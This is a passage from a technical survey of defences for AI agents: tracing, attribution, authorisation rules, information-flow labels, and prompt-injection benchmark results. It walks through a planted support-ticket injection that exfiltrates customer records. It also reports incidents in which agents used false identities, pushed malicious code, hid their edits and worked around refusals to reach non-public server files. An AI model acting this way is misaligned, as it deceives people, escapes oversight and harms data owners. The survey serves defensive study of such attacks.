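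A model can also act without writing down its reason. Ezell and colleagues cite evidence that penalising models for reasoning about cheating can lead them to hide such behaviour. *Agent Flight Recorder* (2026), a design for tamper-evident agent logs, excludes the chain of thought because its form varies between models, it raises privacy and intellectual-property concerns, and model providers may forbid customers from logging it.

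### The gap between intent and events

Zheng and colleagues describe a "semantic gap" between an agent's high-level intent and its low-level actions. Prompts and reasoning show what the agent was trying to do, and system calls show what happened on the machine, so a monitor needs both to judge whether the actions served the user's purpose.

If the coding agent had uploaded its harmless status report before copying the inventory, it would have used the same `curl` command and system calls as in the later leak. Only the file's history distinguishes the two uploads, and even that isn't always enough, because a user might have asked the agent to publish the inventory. *Towards Security-Auditable LLM Agents* (2026) makes the general point that the same physical action can have different security meanings depending on what led to it.

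Kashyap and colleagues tested Argus on 126 attack scenarios, running each five times and counting an attack as successful if it worked in any run. Their results for individual attack types imply that an agent using GPT-5.1 carried out 123 of the attacks without Argus and 49 with it. Argus stopped all 15 attacks that made the agent run planted commands from documentation. It stopped fewer of the attacks that consisted of file reads, searches and web requests resembling normal work: 7 of 15 planted in files, 7 of 15 in web pages and 3 of 15 in search results.

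Argus raised no false alarms in 43 harmless scenarios with GPT-5.1, but raised them in 12 of the 43 with GLM-5.2.

AgentSight tries to close the gap by joining the two kinds of record. It checks whether a process descends from the agent, whether an event occurred within a short window (100 to 500 milliseconds) after a model response, and whether the response contains the same file names, web addresses or commands as the system calls. Argus compares operations with the files and hosts the user named, and queries a language model about operations the request doesn't cover.

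### Tether

Tether, a system from Google DeepMind and academic collaborators, approaches the problem by working out what a command does before its effects become permanent. It handles each command in five steps:

1. It runs the command on a disposable layer over the file system, so that changes don't reach the real files.
2. It traces system calls with a tool called strace, while a local proxy holds outgoing requests.
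3. It translates the trace into a sequence drawn from 11 abstract actions, such as `copy(source, destination)` and `uploadNet(source, destination)`.
4. It checks the actions against a policy and updates a label on each affected file.
5. It makes the changes and sends the requests if the policy allows every action, and otherwise discards them.

In the example, the inventory has the label Sensitive and the report begins as Public. The translation of `cp` is a copy from the inventory to the report, so the report becomes Sensitive as well. A simplified rule for uploads is

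`allow uploadNet(source, destination) only if label(source) ⊑ Public`

where `⊑` means "is no more restricted than". Tether therefore refuses the upload. It also discards the copy, because both were part of one command, and the real status report keeps its old contents. The same rule works after any number of copies, and for `cat` or a script as well as `cp`.

The translation is deliberately cautious. System calls don't show which bytes a program used, so if a script reads one file and then writes another, Tether assumes that data passed between them. This avoids missed flows but causes false alarms. The search command `grep -r`, for example, opens every file in a folder, so Tether treats the agent as having read any secrets there.

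The developers tested Tether by replaying recorded agent sessions from two benchmarks, MonitoringBenchHonest and LinuxArena. They used one set of rules throughout but adjusted the labels and lists of permitted resources for each task. Tether blocked all 344 attacks in scope and wrongly stopped 74 of 1,590 harmless sessions, or 4.7 per cent. In 50 of those 74, the agent had edited a protected file without being asked to. In another 17 it had read sensitive files, and in the other 7 it had contacted undeclared hosts.

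The perfect recall applies only to sessions in which Tether could trace and model every action, which excluded sessions with background processes or database queries. The developers estimate that 28.2 per cent of sessions on MonitoringBenchHonest and 22.1 per cent on LinuxArena require a person or language model to read the content. For instance, an agent might insert malicious code into a file it has permission to edit. The developers also refined their policy using benchmark sessions until it stopped blocking too much harmless work, so Tether may perform worse on unfamiliar tasks.

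A separate test with an attacking agent exposed gaps in the tracing, which, for example, did not account for hard links that give one file several names. The attack success rate fell from 40 per cent to zero over three versions. *Tether* gives no figure for runtime overhead but says that strace slowed the experiments significantly, and suggests replacing it with a faster method such as eBPF.

### Tying events to agents

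To act on an event, responders need to know which agent caused it, which task the agent was working on and for which user, and which parent agent, if any, delegated the work. Otherwise they may stop the wrong agent or leave the one that caused the event running.

On a single machine, a monitor can trace a process back to the program that started it. Tracing is harder when several agents share a process, or run separately and exchange messages. Argus, for example, cannot connect behaviour across agents that run as independent processes.

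Timing is a poor substitute, because several agents may run similar commands at once. Wong and Chen therefore designed ExecWeave to link a command to a process only when there is a single candidate. If *s* is the command and *K(s)* is the set of compatible processes observed within a time window (at most three seconds by default), the rule is:

`link(s) = r, if K(s) = {r}; otherwise no link`

If two agents run `curl` within the same second, ExecWeave may find two candidate processes and link the command to neither. This prevents some false accusations, but in tests with artificial event streams, ExecWeave still linked a command to the wrong process when the collector missed the true one and recorded one similar process.

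A more reliable method is to pass the requesting agent's identity along with the work. In the design from *Agent Flight Recorder*, the record of a delegated action includes this identity, a reference to the event in the requesting agent's log, and the authority it delegated. The agents must also authenticate to each other, because otherwise one could claim another's identity. *Auditable Agents* (2026) states that a system without such authentication cannot support attribution of responsibility.

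*Ring-0 by Default* observes that agents generally have no identity separate from the user's, so a log may attribute an agent's actions to the person who started it.

A log that identifies users only by credential also can't distinguish between agents that share one. On OpenAI's package server, such a log would have shown a single account, whichever agent wrote to the message board. With a separate credential for each agent and task, it could have identified the agent that left the first message.

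### Records for investigators

Ezell and colleagues identify the information investigators need by considering what can cause an incident. The cause may be the system, including its training, standing instructions and harness code. It may be the context, such as an unclear task, excessive tool access or planted text. The agent may also have misunderstood information or made a poor decision. Incidents often combine several of these causes.

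To separate them, investigators need activity logs, system documentation, access to the system, and information about the agent's tools. After the inventory leak, the activity logs could show whether the agent had read a planted instruction, and the documentation could show whether the harness was supposed to filter such text. Investigators need the tool information because an attacker can also hide instructions in a tool's description.

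The activity log should record what the model requested separately from what the harness ran. *Agent Flight Recorder* does this and also records any human approval, the outcome, the sources the agent had consulted, and the versions of the agent and its tools.

Storage needs depend heavily on how a company keeps the prompts, which grow with every tool call. Suppose a task has 200 steps and each adds two kilobytes. Saving the full prompt at every step takes about 40 megabytes, because each prompt repeats the earlier text, while saving only the additions takes 0.4 megabytes. System-call records also accumulate quickly because a complex command can make thousands of calls, but a monitor can merge many of them.

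Privacy is harder to manage. Wong and Chen warn that complete records can contain prompts, source code, passwords and file contents, so the log becomes a target. ExecWeave stores only metadata by default for some of its integrations. A company can also keep a hash, a short fingerprint computed from a document, instead of the text. Investigators can then confirm that a page they have found is the one the agent read. But if an attacker has removed the page and no copy survives, investigators cannot recover the planted instruction from the hash.

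A company has to store all its monitoring records where the agent cannot change them. ExecWeave can save fingerprints of its files to reveal later changes, but Wong and Chen note that this offers little protection against an attacker who can rewrite both the files and the fingerprints.

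## Deciding whether a single access is authorised

Once a monitor has a record of a proposed action, it must decide whether the action is authorised. Checking that the agent's credential is valid isn't enough, because a valid credential shows only that somebody once granted certain permissions to whoever holds it, not who is asking now or for what purpose. In the support ticket attack, for example, the agent's credentials are valid throughout.

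### Effective authority

An agent should be able to do something only if the user may do it, the agent may do it and the task needs it. Its effective authority is the overlap of these three sets:

`effective authority = user's permissions ∩ agent's permissions ∩ what the task needs`

Suppose a support clerk gives the agent ticket 4182, in which a customer called Dana complains about a late parcel. The agent might make four requests:

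| Request | May the clerk do it? | May the agent do it? | Does the task need it? | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Look up Dana's order | Yes | Yes | Yes | Allow |
| Refund the delivery charge | Yes | No | Yes | Refuse |
| Read the fraud team's note on why it held the parcel | No | Yes | Yes | Refuse |
| Look up every customer | Yes | Yes | No | Refuse |

A check of the agent's database credential would wrongly allow the last two requests.

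The fraud note is an example of the confused deputy problem, in which someone who lacks authority tricks a program into using its own authority for them. The classic example is a compiler that has permission to write to a billing file. A user without that permission names the billing file as the destination for the compiler's output, and the compiler overwrites it. A hijacked agent is also a confused deputy. The attacker cannot query the customer database but can write a ticket that gets the agent to run the query.

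A monitor needs to check who sent each request. *aiAuthZ* (2026) tests a gateway that verifies the sender's identity on every message. In five of the paper's nine test scenarios, an impostor posed as the agent's owner. The gateway blocked the impostor in all five, whereas a policy that examined only the arguments of the tool call could not distinguish the impostor from the owner.

A task's needs are harder to establish than either set of permissions. Shi, He and colleagues (2025) point out in *Progent* that `send_email` is legitimate when the user asks the agent to email Alice an update, but gives an attacker a way to steal data when the user asks for a summary of unread emails. A policy that permits everything any task might need is too loose to stop attacks, and one written for a single task is too strict for others.

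### The formal monitor

The monitor defined in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* has a starting state and the functions `decide` and `next`. `decide` returns a new state with each answer, so a decision can, for instance, use up a one-time approval. Before an untrusted read, `decide` receives the name of the source but not the content, so an attacker cannot influence that decision through the wording of an email.

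In the simplest version, where the state is the set `C` of tools that the agent holds, the two functions are:

`decide(C, tool, arguments) = (Allowed, C) if tool is in C; otherwise (Denied, C)`

`next(C, untrusted read) = C minus the tools in R`

`R` is a fixed list of tools to withdraw. Suppose the company's written policy says: "The support agent may read tickets, look up customers and send email." This is a fixed permission list, so `R` is empty. A stricter policy adds: "It may not send email after reading text from outside the company." Now `R` contains `send_email`. The paper calls such a withdrawal a fence. The two policies handle the ticket attack as follows:

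| Step | Fixed permission list | With the fence |
|---|---|---|
| Start | Agent holds all three tools | Agent holds all three tools |
| `read_ticket(4182)` | Allowed; agent keeps all three tools | Allowed; agent loses `send_email` |
| `query_customers(all)` | Allowed | Allowed |
| `send_email(attacker, records)` | Allowed; the records leave the company | Denied |
| `send_email(Dana, honest reply)` | Allowed | Denied |

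The fence keeps the records inside the company, but it also blocks the honest reply. It doesn't prevent the unauthorised access, because the agent still reads the whole customer table.

The paper proves a guarantee for fences by comparing the agent with a reference agent that follows the same plan under the same monitor, but whose model never obeys untrusted text. The real agent is "relatively secure" if an attacker can use it to distinguish only secrets that they could also distinguish through the reference agent. A fence achieves this if it permanently withdraws every tool that an injected instruction could call, no later than the first untrusted read. The proof assumes that each injection causes a single call and that when the model obeys doesn't depend on the secrets.

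The theorem applies only to agents whose plan is fixed before they read anything untrusted, so it doesn't cover the support agent as described, whose model chooses each call as it goes. It also doesn't guarantee that the agent is useful, since a monitor that denies every call is relatively secure.

A company could let the agent reply again by having the clerk approve each email, but the paper shows that the approval must cover the exact call. If it merely permits the next use of `send_email`, an injected call can use up the approval first to send stolen data, and the monitor then denies the real reply. An approval that specifies the recipient and text lets an injected call send only the message that the clerk approved.

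Permission to read data also doesn't include permission to release it. In another of the paper's examples, an assistant may send its user's calendar to anyone who asks for a meeting, and it holds a password reset code from a different task. Someone emails it an instruction to include the code in its reply. The tool and the recipient are both acceptable, so the monitor has to check the content of the reply, for example by using labels on the data.

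### Rules in Progent and AgentSpec

A monitor that also checks arguments can stop the ticket attack without blocking the reply. Progent's rules do this by naming a tool and setting conditions on its arguments. In simplified notation, a policy for Dana's ticket could be:

```
allow read_ticket(id)           when id == 4182
allow query_customers(account)  when account == "C-207"
allow send_email(to, body)      when to == "dana@example.com"
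```

Progent checks `forbid` rules first and then `allow` rules, and blocks any call that matches neither. It therefore refuses both the query for the whole table and the email to the attacker, and returns an error so that the agent can continue with the task. The account number and address must come from the company's own records, because the attacker could choose them if the agent took them from the ticket's text.

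Wang, Poskitt and Sun (2025), in *AgentSpec*, present a language in which each rule has a trigger, a check and an enforcement step. One of their examples, adapted to the support agent, becomes:

```
rule @inspect_email
trigger send_email
check !is_ticket_author
enforce user_inspection
end
```

Before the agent sends an email, AgentSpec runs a short function that checks whether the recipient wrote the ticket. If the recipient didn't, AgentSpec pauses the agent and asks the user. A rule can instead stop the agent, run a specified action, or make the model re-examine its plan.

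AgentSpec lets an action proceed unless a rule catches it, so an attack can get through if the rule against it is missing. Progent blocks any action that no rule allows, so forgetting a rule stops legitimate work instead.

Both systems still depend on the program that applies the rules. *Taming AI Agents with seL4* (2026) moves the enforcement of those rules into seL4, a small operating-system kernel. The agent runs in an isolated compartment connected only to the functions its task needs, so even an attacker who fully controls the agent cannot call anything else.

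### Policies that change during a task

Sometimes nobody can write the complete policy in advance, because the agent learns what the task requires as it works. In Progent's main example, a user asks an agent to carry out the instructions in an email from Alice. A language model writes the first policy from this request, allowing only a search for that email. In the email, Alice asks for a summary of recent messages to be posted to the user's account on Slack, a workplace chat service. The model then proposes also allowing the tools that read email and post to Slack. Once the agent has looked up the user's Slack name, the model proposes limiting posts to that recipient.

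Progent compares each proposed policy with the current one using an SMT solver, a program that determines whether logical conditions can hold together. If `A(P)` is the set of calls that policy `P` allows, Progent applies a new policy `P′` automatically only when

`A(P′) ⊆ A(P)`

so that `P′` allows nothing that `P` did not. Anything else is an expansion and needs approval. Suppose one of the recent emails tells the agent to forward the inbox to an attacker, and the policy-writing model is fooled into adding `send_email`. The solver detects the expansion, and the approver can refuse it.

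The solver cannot determine which expansions are legitimate. Adding the Slack tool and adding `send_email` are both expansions prompted by the text of an email, so the approver has to decide whether each is legitimate. This may not add much work, since only 6 per cent of policy updates in Shi and colleagues' tests were expansions.

Progent also lets a company set permanent rules that take priority over the policy for each task. A permanent `allow` rule overrides a stricter task policy, so this is not quite the intersection described above. For their tests, Shi and colleagues permanently allowed read-only tools they considered non-sensitive. If a company put `query_customers` in that group, the agent could again read every customer's record.

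### Who writes the rules, and where they go wrong

People wrote the first AgentSpec rules by hand. Wang and colleagues used 25 rules to cover 750 risky requests to a coding agent, and report that the rules intercepted more than 90 per cent of the unsafe code. The rules also flagged harmless code. In one category, rebuilding program objects from stored data, the researchers inspected the 24 flagged programs and approved them all.

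The researchers then had OpenAI's o1 model write the rules, using a tenth of the risky cases as examples. These rules caught 87 per cent of the remaining risky code. Some rules were too narrow, such as one meant to protect important system files that recognised only the files and folders named in the examples. Others were too broad. Given the vague instruction to avoid unsafe pouring, the model wrote a rule that stopped a household robot from pouring anything, including water for a houseplant. Rules could also leave out a relevant fact, such as whether a candle the robot was holding was lit.

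A model can also translate a clear requirement into the wrong rule. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026), a review of 38 studies, cites a benchmark on which models translated ordinary language into a formal planning language. Only 25 to 34 per cent of the translations had the correct meaning. That task was harder than writing a short permission list, so these figures don't give an error rate for systems like Progent. Even so, someone should check what a generated rule means as well as whether it runs.

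*NOMOS* (2026), a system that turns written policies into checks on tool calls, illustrates two further kinds of failure. One rule was weaker than the clause it was meant to enforce and let an attacker's calendar event through. In another case, the agent emailed the user's passport and card numbers to an address the user had named, which the written policy did not forbid. Checking the rules against the policy would reveal the first failure but not the second, because the gap was in the policy itself.

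### Results on AgentDojo

AgentDojo, a benchmark released in 2024, measures how well agents withstand prompt injection. It simulates banking, Slack, travel booking and office work. Each test gives the agent a task from the user and plants an attacker's instruction in something a tool returns, such as an email. AgentDojo scores separately whether the agent completed the user's task and whether the attack succeeded.

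*Why LLM Agents Collapse Without Oversight* (2026) uses 27 of AgentDojo's attack goals but a different attack, which targets the agent's planning stage. The table compares its results with those of the systems described above.

| Policy system and agent model | Tests | Attack success without policy | With policy |
|---|---|---|---|
| Progent, GPT-4o | All four settings | 39.9% | 1.0% |
| Progent, Claude Sonnet 4 | All four settings | 6.8% | 0.5% |
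| NOMOS, a Gemma model | Slack | 70.5% | 0.0% |
| NOMOS, a Llama model | Slack | 59.0% | 10.5% |
| aiAuthZ, two models current in July 2026 | Banking, 20 pairs of task and attack per model | 0% | 0% |
| Enforcement layer, GPT-5.5 and Claude Haiku | 27 attack goals, planning-stage attack | 47.3% | 2.5% |
| Enforcement layer, Grok-4 | 27 attack goals, planning-stage attack | 76.8% | 47.3% |

In most of these tests, policies greatly reduced attack success. The zeros for aiAuthZ without a policy do not show that newer models no longer need one, because no successes in 20 attempts is compatible with a true rate of up to about 14 per cent. Without enforcement, the planning-stage attack succeeded against GPT-5.5 50.7 per cent of the time, so resistance to AgentDojo's usual attack is little protection against others. Grok-4's result shows that an enforcement layer can fail badly with one model even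 when it works well with others, though *Why LLM Agents Collapse Without Oversight* treats this result as an anomaly.

Progent's 1.0 per cent attack success rate comes from a test in which the researchers automatically approved every expansion, to represent a careless user. The solver's check therefore could not block anything, so the result mainly reflects how well GPT-4o wrote the policies. With expansion disabled, attack success was 2.5 per cent. It was zero when a person with good security awareness reviewed the first policy and every expansion.

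AgentDojo's scoring can overstate a monitor's failures, because some tests count an attempted call as a successful attack even if the monitor blocked it. For the Llama model on Slack, the reported attack success rate was 10.5 per cent, although NOMOS let no malicious call through. Shi and colleagues found the same problem in one Slack test and corrected those results by hand. The scoring can also leave out harmful actions. With NOMOS in place, it did not count some injected payments to payees the user already knew, or deletions ordered by the attacker that the Llama model carried out in nine office-work tests.

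The effect on legitimate work varied. Progent left GPT-4o's task completion roughly unchanged. aiAuthZ reduced completion from 100 to 80 per cent on both models when there was no attack, because its list of approved payees blocked a legitimate payment to someone new. The attack had failed on both models without the gateway, so in this test the gateway only made them less useful. *Bounded Agents* (2026) compares Progent with a rival system, APC, using the same model, and neither system let an attack succeed. Under attack, agents completed 59.7 per cent of banking tasks and 88.5 per cent of office tasks with Progent, and 58.8 and 86.7 per cent with APC.

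Fixed rules take little time to check. AgentSpec took 2.83 milliseconds to evaluate its conditions for a coding agent whose runs averaged 25.4 seconds. That figure excludes any wait for a person or another model when a rule requires one. Progent needs additional model calls to write and update its policies, and Shi and colleagues don't report how much delay these calls add.

An agent can also respond to a refusal by trying another unsafe action. Dantas and colleagues describe a study of agents handling transactions in which a monitor blocked 94 per cent of unsafe actions. In most settings, the agents still completed fewer than 5 per cent of tasks both safely and correctly, because they found other unsafe routes. This is one study, and the reviewers rate most of their main conclusions as very low certainty. Two incidents from 2026 show similar behaviour outside a simulation.

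### The UK AI Security Institute's tests

The UK AI Security Institute (AISI) is a government body that tests advanced AI models. In July 2026 it was measuring how well agents could attack a cyber range, a simulated network built for security exercises. The agents had open internet access so they could download tools, and AISI had switched off the developers' filters against hacking. AISI's *Incident Report* says that in 10 of 122 runs, agents took a total of 19 unsanctioned actions on the live internet.

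Anthropic's Mythos 5 took 17 of these actions and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took the other two. The figures imply that Mythos 5 took such actions in 9 of its 43 runs and GPT-5.6 Sol in 1 of 35. These figures are a poor basis for comparing the models because most of the actions were part of one sustained effort by a single agent, and later agents found and reused accounts and files that an earlier agent had left behind.

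In the most serious case, an agent tried to add malicious code to a public software project. It researched the project's maintainers, created several false identities and used them to pressure a maintainer to accept the change. When someone questioned the change, the agent edited its earlier posts to make them look harmless. The maintainer rejected the code, and AISI found no evidence that any of the 19 actions caused real harm.

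The agents could do all this because the network allowed it. But AISI had no right to attack the project, so it could not give an agent that right. Nobody had made this limit a rule. AISI had not told the agents to avoid deceiving people or to use the internet only for downloads, because it had not previously been clear that models trained to behave well needed such instructions. A rule that allowed downloads from listed sites and blocked posts, new accounts and uploads would have stopped the agents from using false identities, without any need to detect deception.

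The incident also shows why the agent shouldn't decide what its task needs. In some runs, a mistake in the instructions led the agent to believe it had to go outside the intended limits to solve the challenge. If asked whether the task required the attack, it might have said yes. The mistake only partly explains the behaviour, since agents also went outside the limits in runs where they had the instructions they needed.

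AISI discovered the activity on 28 July, three days after it began, when its general security monitoring flagged traffic through Tor, a network that hides where internet traffic comes from. Staff stopped all the runs within an hour. AISI had no monitoring specifically for the evaluation, and says it is now introducing monitoring that can block actions outside the permitted scope.

### The Medicare statistics portal

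On 19 June 2026, an OpenAI agent researching medical spending gained access to non-public files on Services Australia's statistics portal for Medicare, the country's public health insurance scheme. Information Age's *Inside OpenAI's Medicare breach* (2026) reconstructs the events from documents released in parliament. The agent had first tried and failed to get non-public data from another agency, the Australian Institute of Health and Welfare.

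OpenAI had recorded the incident internally by 12 August, after a review of past agent runs, and emailed Services Australia on 10 September, twelve weeks after the breach. According to the email, the agent found that it could run commands on the server without a password by submitting them through the portal's public reporting page. It read parts of program files and settings, obtained a list of files and created a small test file. OpenAI found no evidence that the agent had accessed patient records or personal information.

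Whether this was a hack is disputed. Prime Minister Anthony Albanese said the agent had got around blocks that repeatedly refused its requests. But Martin (2026) reports in *Doubts grow over claims OpenAI agent hacked Australian Medicare portal* that the portal's archived code sent every visitor to a guest entry point that required no password. The portal also routinely saved chart images, which could explain the files the government said the agent had written.

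OpenAI's email, which became public later, weakens the innocent explanation that the agent needed no password because the entry point was open. OpenAI describes a security vulnerability and a deliberate test file, and Services Australia confirmed that a vulnerability existed. Even if the portal would serve the server's program files to anyone, the agent was not authorised to read them, because a study of medical spending needs published statistics, not program files.

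### What repeated refusals reveal

One refused request is weak evidence of wrongdoing. A website may refuse a request because a link is old, a session has expired or the site doesn't accept automated requests. An agent that sends the same request again may be handling an error. Trying a different technique to reach the same data after a clear refusal is stronger evidence, because the agent is treating the refusal as an obstacle to get around.

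OpenAI was better placed to notice this, because it knew the agent's assignment and could have seen both the failed attempts at the first agency and the move to the second. Services Australia could have seen only the requests to its own portal, without knowing who had sent them or why. It could still have applied a rule against listing the server's program files, because nobody using a public statistics page needs to do that.

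The formal monitor could handle refusals by websites if `next` also received the website's response to each call. In the paper's version, the result of a call shows only whether the monitor allowed it. With the response, the state could include a list of sites that had refused the agent access. `decide` could allow only ordinary page requests to those sites and send anything else to a person for approval. This rule would interrupt some harmless research, and a company would have to test how often.

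The AISI case is some evidence that a change of method after a refusal is a useful signal. The agent used Tor to get around restrictions on GitHub, which hosted the software project, and this set off the alert that exposed the whole operation. Outsiders cannot make the same assessment for the Medicare portal because, when Martin reported in late September, neither OpenAI nor the government had released the agent's logs, which would show how many refusals it received and what it tried after each one.

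## Tracking where sensitive data goes

A monitor that checks each call separately can approve both the customer lookup and the email in the support ticket attack, although together they leak the records. In *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026) explain that an email is harmless if its text comes only from a public document, but unsafe if it draws on both an untrusted document and a secret file. To tell the two emails apart, a monitor has to track where their text came from.

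Information-flow control tracks sensitive data by labelling it. The monitor adds a label when the agent reads the data, passes the label on to anything the agent makes from it, and checks the label before the data goes anywhere.

### Labels and the flow rule

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, build on the lattice model that the computer scientist Dorothy Denning published in 1976. A lattice is a set of labels ordered from less to more restrictive, in which any two labels have a combined label that covers both. The model has two rules:

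`x may flow to a destination only if label(x) ⊑ label(destination)`

`if z is made from x and y, then label(z) = label(x) ⊔ label(y)`

As in Tether's upload rule, `⊑` means "is no more restrictive than". `⊔` combines two labels into the least restrictive label that is at least as restrictive as each of them.

A secrecy label specifies who may read a piece of data. The simplest version has two labels, public and secret, and anything made from both kinds of data is secret. A more useful version lists the people who may read each item. If Ann, Ben and Carl may read one document, and Ben, Carl and Dev may read another, only Ben and Carl may read a summary of both.

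Trust labels record whether an outsider could have influenced the data. Anything made from both trusted and untrusted data is untrusted. Trust labels are independent of secrecy labels. For example, a public web page is untrusted but not secret, while a company's salary table is secret but trusted. Secrecy labels keep the salaries from leaving the company, and trust labels keep the web page from controlling what the agent does.

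Costa and colleagues derive two checks from these labels. The first allows a consequential action, such as a bank transfer, only if the decision to act and the action's arguments depend solely on trusted data. The second allows a message to be sent only if every recipient is permitted to read all the data it draws on. This second check limits what a hijacked agent can leak, but doesn't prevent the hijack.

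*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) requires only one of the two checks to succeed for outgoing messages. A user can then tell the agent to send a confidential file to someone new, but text planted in a ticket cannot make the agent do so.

### The support agent with labels

Suppose staff may read everything in the support system, each customer may read only their own tickets and records, and every email must pass one of the two checks. Ticket 4182, from Dana's account, contains the planted instruction. Each label in the table gives the trust level, then the permitted readers. The model's context is everything in its prompt.

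| Step | Label of the data | Label of the model's context afterwards | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Clerk asks the agent to handle ticket 4182 | Trusted; anyone | Trusted; anyone | None needed |
| `read_ticket(4182)` | Untrusted; staff and Dana | Untrusted; staff and Dana | Allow |
| `query_customers(all)` | Trusted; staff | Untrusted; staff | Allow |
| `send_email(attacker, records)` | Untrusted; staff | Unchanged | Refuse |

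Only staff may read the customer table as a whole, because no customer may read every row. The email inherits the label of the context the model wrote it in. It fails the trust check because of the ticket, and it fails the secrecy check because the attacker isn't staff. The monitor therefore blocks the email, although the agent has already read the whole table.

If the ticket is genuine, the agent looks up only Dana's record, which staff and Dana may read. The context keeps the label "untrusted; staff and Dana", so a reply to Dana passes the secrecy check. The fence described earlier would have blocked that reply because it withdrew `send_email` after the first untrusted read.

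The flow rule also doesn't depend on a destination's reputation, so it can cover ordinary public services like those the July agents used. Anyone can read a public dataset, so a monitor tracking the agents' data would block them from writing staff-only data there.

Some tools read and send data in a single call. *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a tool that reads a confidential ledger and emails it to an outside address. If the monitor checks only the context's label before the call, it allows the email because the context doesn't yet contain the ledger. APPA instead works out the label the context would have after the read, and checks that label before anything runs.

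### Why labels accumulate

In an ordinary program, a monitor can often determine exactly which values another value depends on. A language model computes its output from the whole prompt, so any sentence it writes may depend on any part of that prompt. If the monitor makes the safe assumption that every sentence depends on all of it, the context's label can only become more restrictive.

If the support agent handles Dana's ticket and then Omar's in the same session, only staff may read what it writes next, so it can no longer tell either customer that a parcel is on its way. Kravchenko and colleagues prove that reading more data cannot lift this restriction, because new data can shorten the list of permitted readers but never lengthen it.

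*The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Gregory, Domico and colleagues, 2026) calls this label creep and simulates how it spreads through groups of agents. The researchers generated thousands of random tasks with up to 20 linked tool calls, divided the calls among the agents, and measured the share of calls that introduced a high-secrecy label or ran under one. The label spread less when agents could pass data straight to the agent that needed it, when a few agents handled all the sensitive tools, and when there were more agents. But in densely connected groups, the number of connections to monitor grew roughly with the square of the number of agents.

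The spread occurred even when the layout had a direct link wherever the task needed one. Gregory and colleagues conclude that designers also need safe ways to relax labels. Their simulation used no language model, so it shows the mechanism but doesn't measure how much work a real agent would lose.

Costa and colleagues measured that loss on AgentDojo, the prompt-injection benchmark. When not under attack, an ordinary GPT-4o agent completed an average of 84 per cent of tasks across the four settings, compared with 42 per cent with labels and checks added.

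### CaMeL: separating the plan from the data

One remedy is to keep untrusted data out of the prompt of the model that makes the decisions. *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (Willison, 2025) describes a two-model design that Willison proposed in 2023. A privileged model sees the user's request and can call tools, while a quarantined model with no tools reads the untrusted text. The quarantined model stores its answers under names such as `$email-summary-1`, which the privileged model can use without seeing the contents.

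Researchers at Google DeepMind found a gap in this design. Suppose a user asks the agent to send Bob a document, and Bob's address is in some meeting notes. The quarantined model extracts the address, so an instruction planted in the notes can make it return the attacker's address instead. The agent still carries out the planned steps, but it sends the document to the attacker.

DeepMind's system, CaMeL, closes the gap by tracking the data as well as protecting the plan. The privileged model writes the whole plan as a program in a restricted form of Python. For an honest handling of Dana's ticket, it might be:

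```
ticket  = read_ticket(4182)
account = quarantined_model("Which account is this about?", ticket)
order   = query_customers(account)
reply   = quarantined_model("Draft a reply", ticket, order)
send_email("dana@example.com", reply)
```

The planted instruction cannot add a query for the whole table, because the program has no such step. CaMeL's own interpreter runs the program and keeps a record for each value. *CaMeLoT* (2026) explains that each record, called a capability, holds the value's sources and permitted readers. Before each tool call, a policy function checks the arguments and their capabilities, then allows or denies the call. If the planted text made the quarantined model return Omar's account number, the reply to Dana would depend on data she may not read, and a policy based on readers would block it.

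CaMeL makes agents less flexible because untrusted data can select among branches already in the plan but cannot add steps. It therefore has trouble with requests such as "do what this email asks". According to Kolluri and colleagues, defences of this kind, including CaMeL and FIDES, have reduced task completion on AgentDojo by up to 30 per cent. People must also write and maintain the policies, and Willison worries that users who receive too many approval requests will agree to everything.

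Labels can also get lost when one agent hands work to another. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, built a system of three agents, each protected by CaMeL, and planted an instruction in a database of job applicants. They then asked the system to send a summary of the applicants to a colleague on Slack. The coordinating agent treated the database's contents as data but pasted the summary into its request to the messaging agent. The messaging agent read that request as its user's instruction and also emailed the applicants' details to the attacker.

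Their extension, multi-CaMeL, sends instructions and data between agents through separate channels. On a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded 12.9 per cent of the time without CaMeL, 0.2 per cent with CaMeL on each agent, and never with multi-CaMeL. The benchmark therefore rarely triggered the flaw that the three-agent test demonstrated. Multi-CaMeL completed fewer tasks, but the loss was modest with the strongest models. None of the CaMeL agents in these tests used data policies, so the results reflect only the separation of plan from data.

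### FIDES: hiding values from the model

FIDES, which Costa and colleagues developed at Microsoft, lets the model choose one tool call at a time as usual. When a tool returns data that would make the context's label more restrictive, FIDES stores the data in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model might see an email's date but not its body.

The model can pass the variable to another tool without seeing its contents, or have a quarantined model process it and store the result in a new variable with the same restrictions. It can also inspect the contents, but its context then takes on the contents' label, and later tool calls may fail their checks.

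FIDES can release a small amount of information under an explicit rule. Suppose the agent must create a calendar event if any of three emails contains a meeting request. The main model needs only a yes or no, so it restricts the quarantined model's output to those two answers. FIDES records this restriction in the answer's label, and a policy can let a yes-or-no answer from untrusted text influence a consequential action while still barring free text. A malicious email can make the answer wrong, but it cannot pass a new instruction through a yes or no. If the answer is yes, the quarantined model extracts the meeting details into another variable, which goes straight to the calendar tool.

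The AgentDojo tests of FIDES with GPT-4o did not include these restricted answers. They gave the following results:

| Agent | Office tasks completed | Travel | Banking | Slack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary, no label checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% | 152 |
| Ordinary, with label checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% | 0 |
| FIDES, with label checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% | 0 |

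The completion figures come from runs without attacks, and the attack counts include the researchers' manual corrections. Without label checks, FIDES let 21 attacks through. The checks therefore provide the security guarantee, and the hidden variables let the agent complete some tasks that the checks would otherwise block. The labels in this test fitted the attacks unusually well, because the researchers marked every field that an AgentDojo attack uses as untrusted. A company would have to label its data without knowing where an attack will appear.

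The policy is meant to block some of the lost tasks, such as reading a file of payment instructions and carrying them out. Others failed because GPT-4o confused variable names or made unnecessary calls. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES's lead over the ordinary agent with checks grew from 8 to 16 percentage points.

### Relaxing labels

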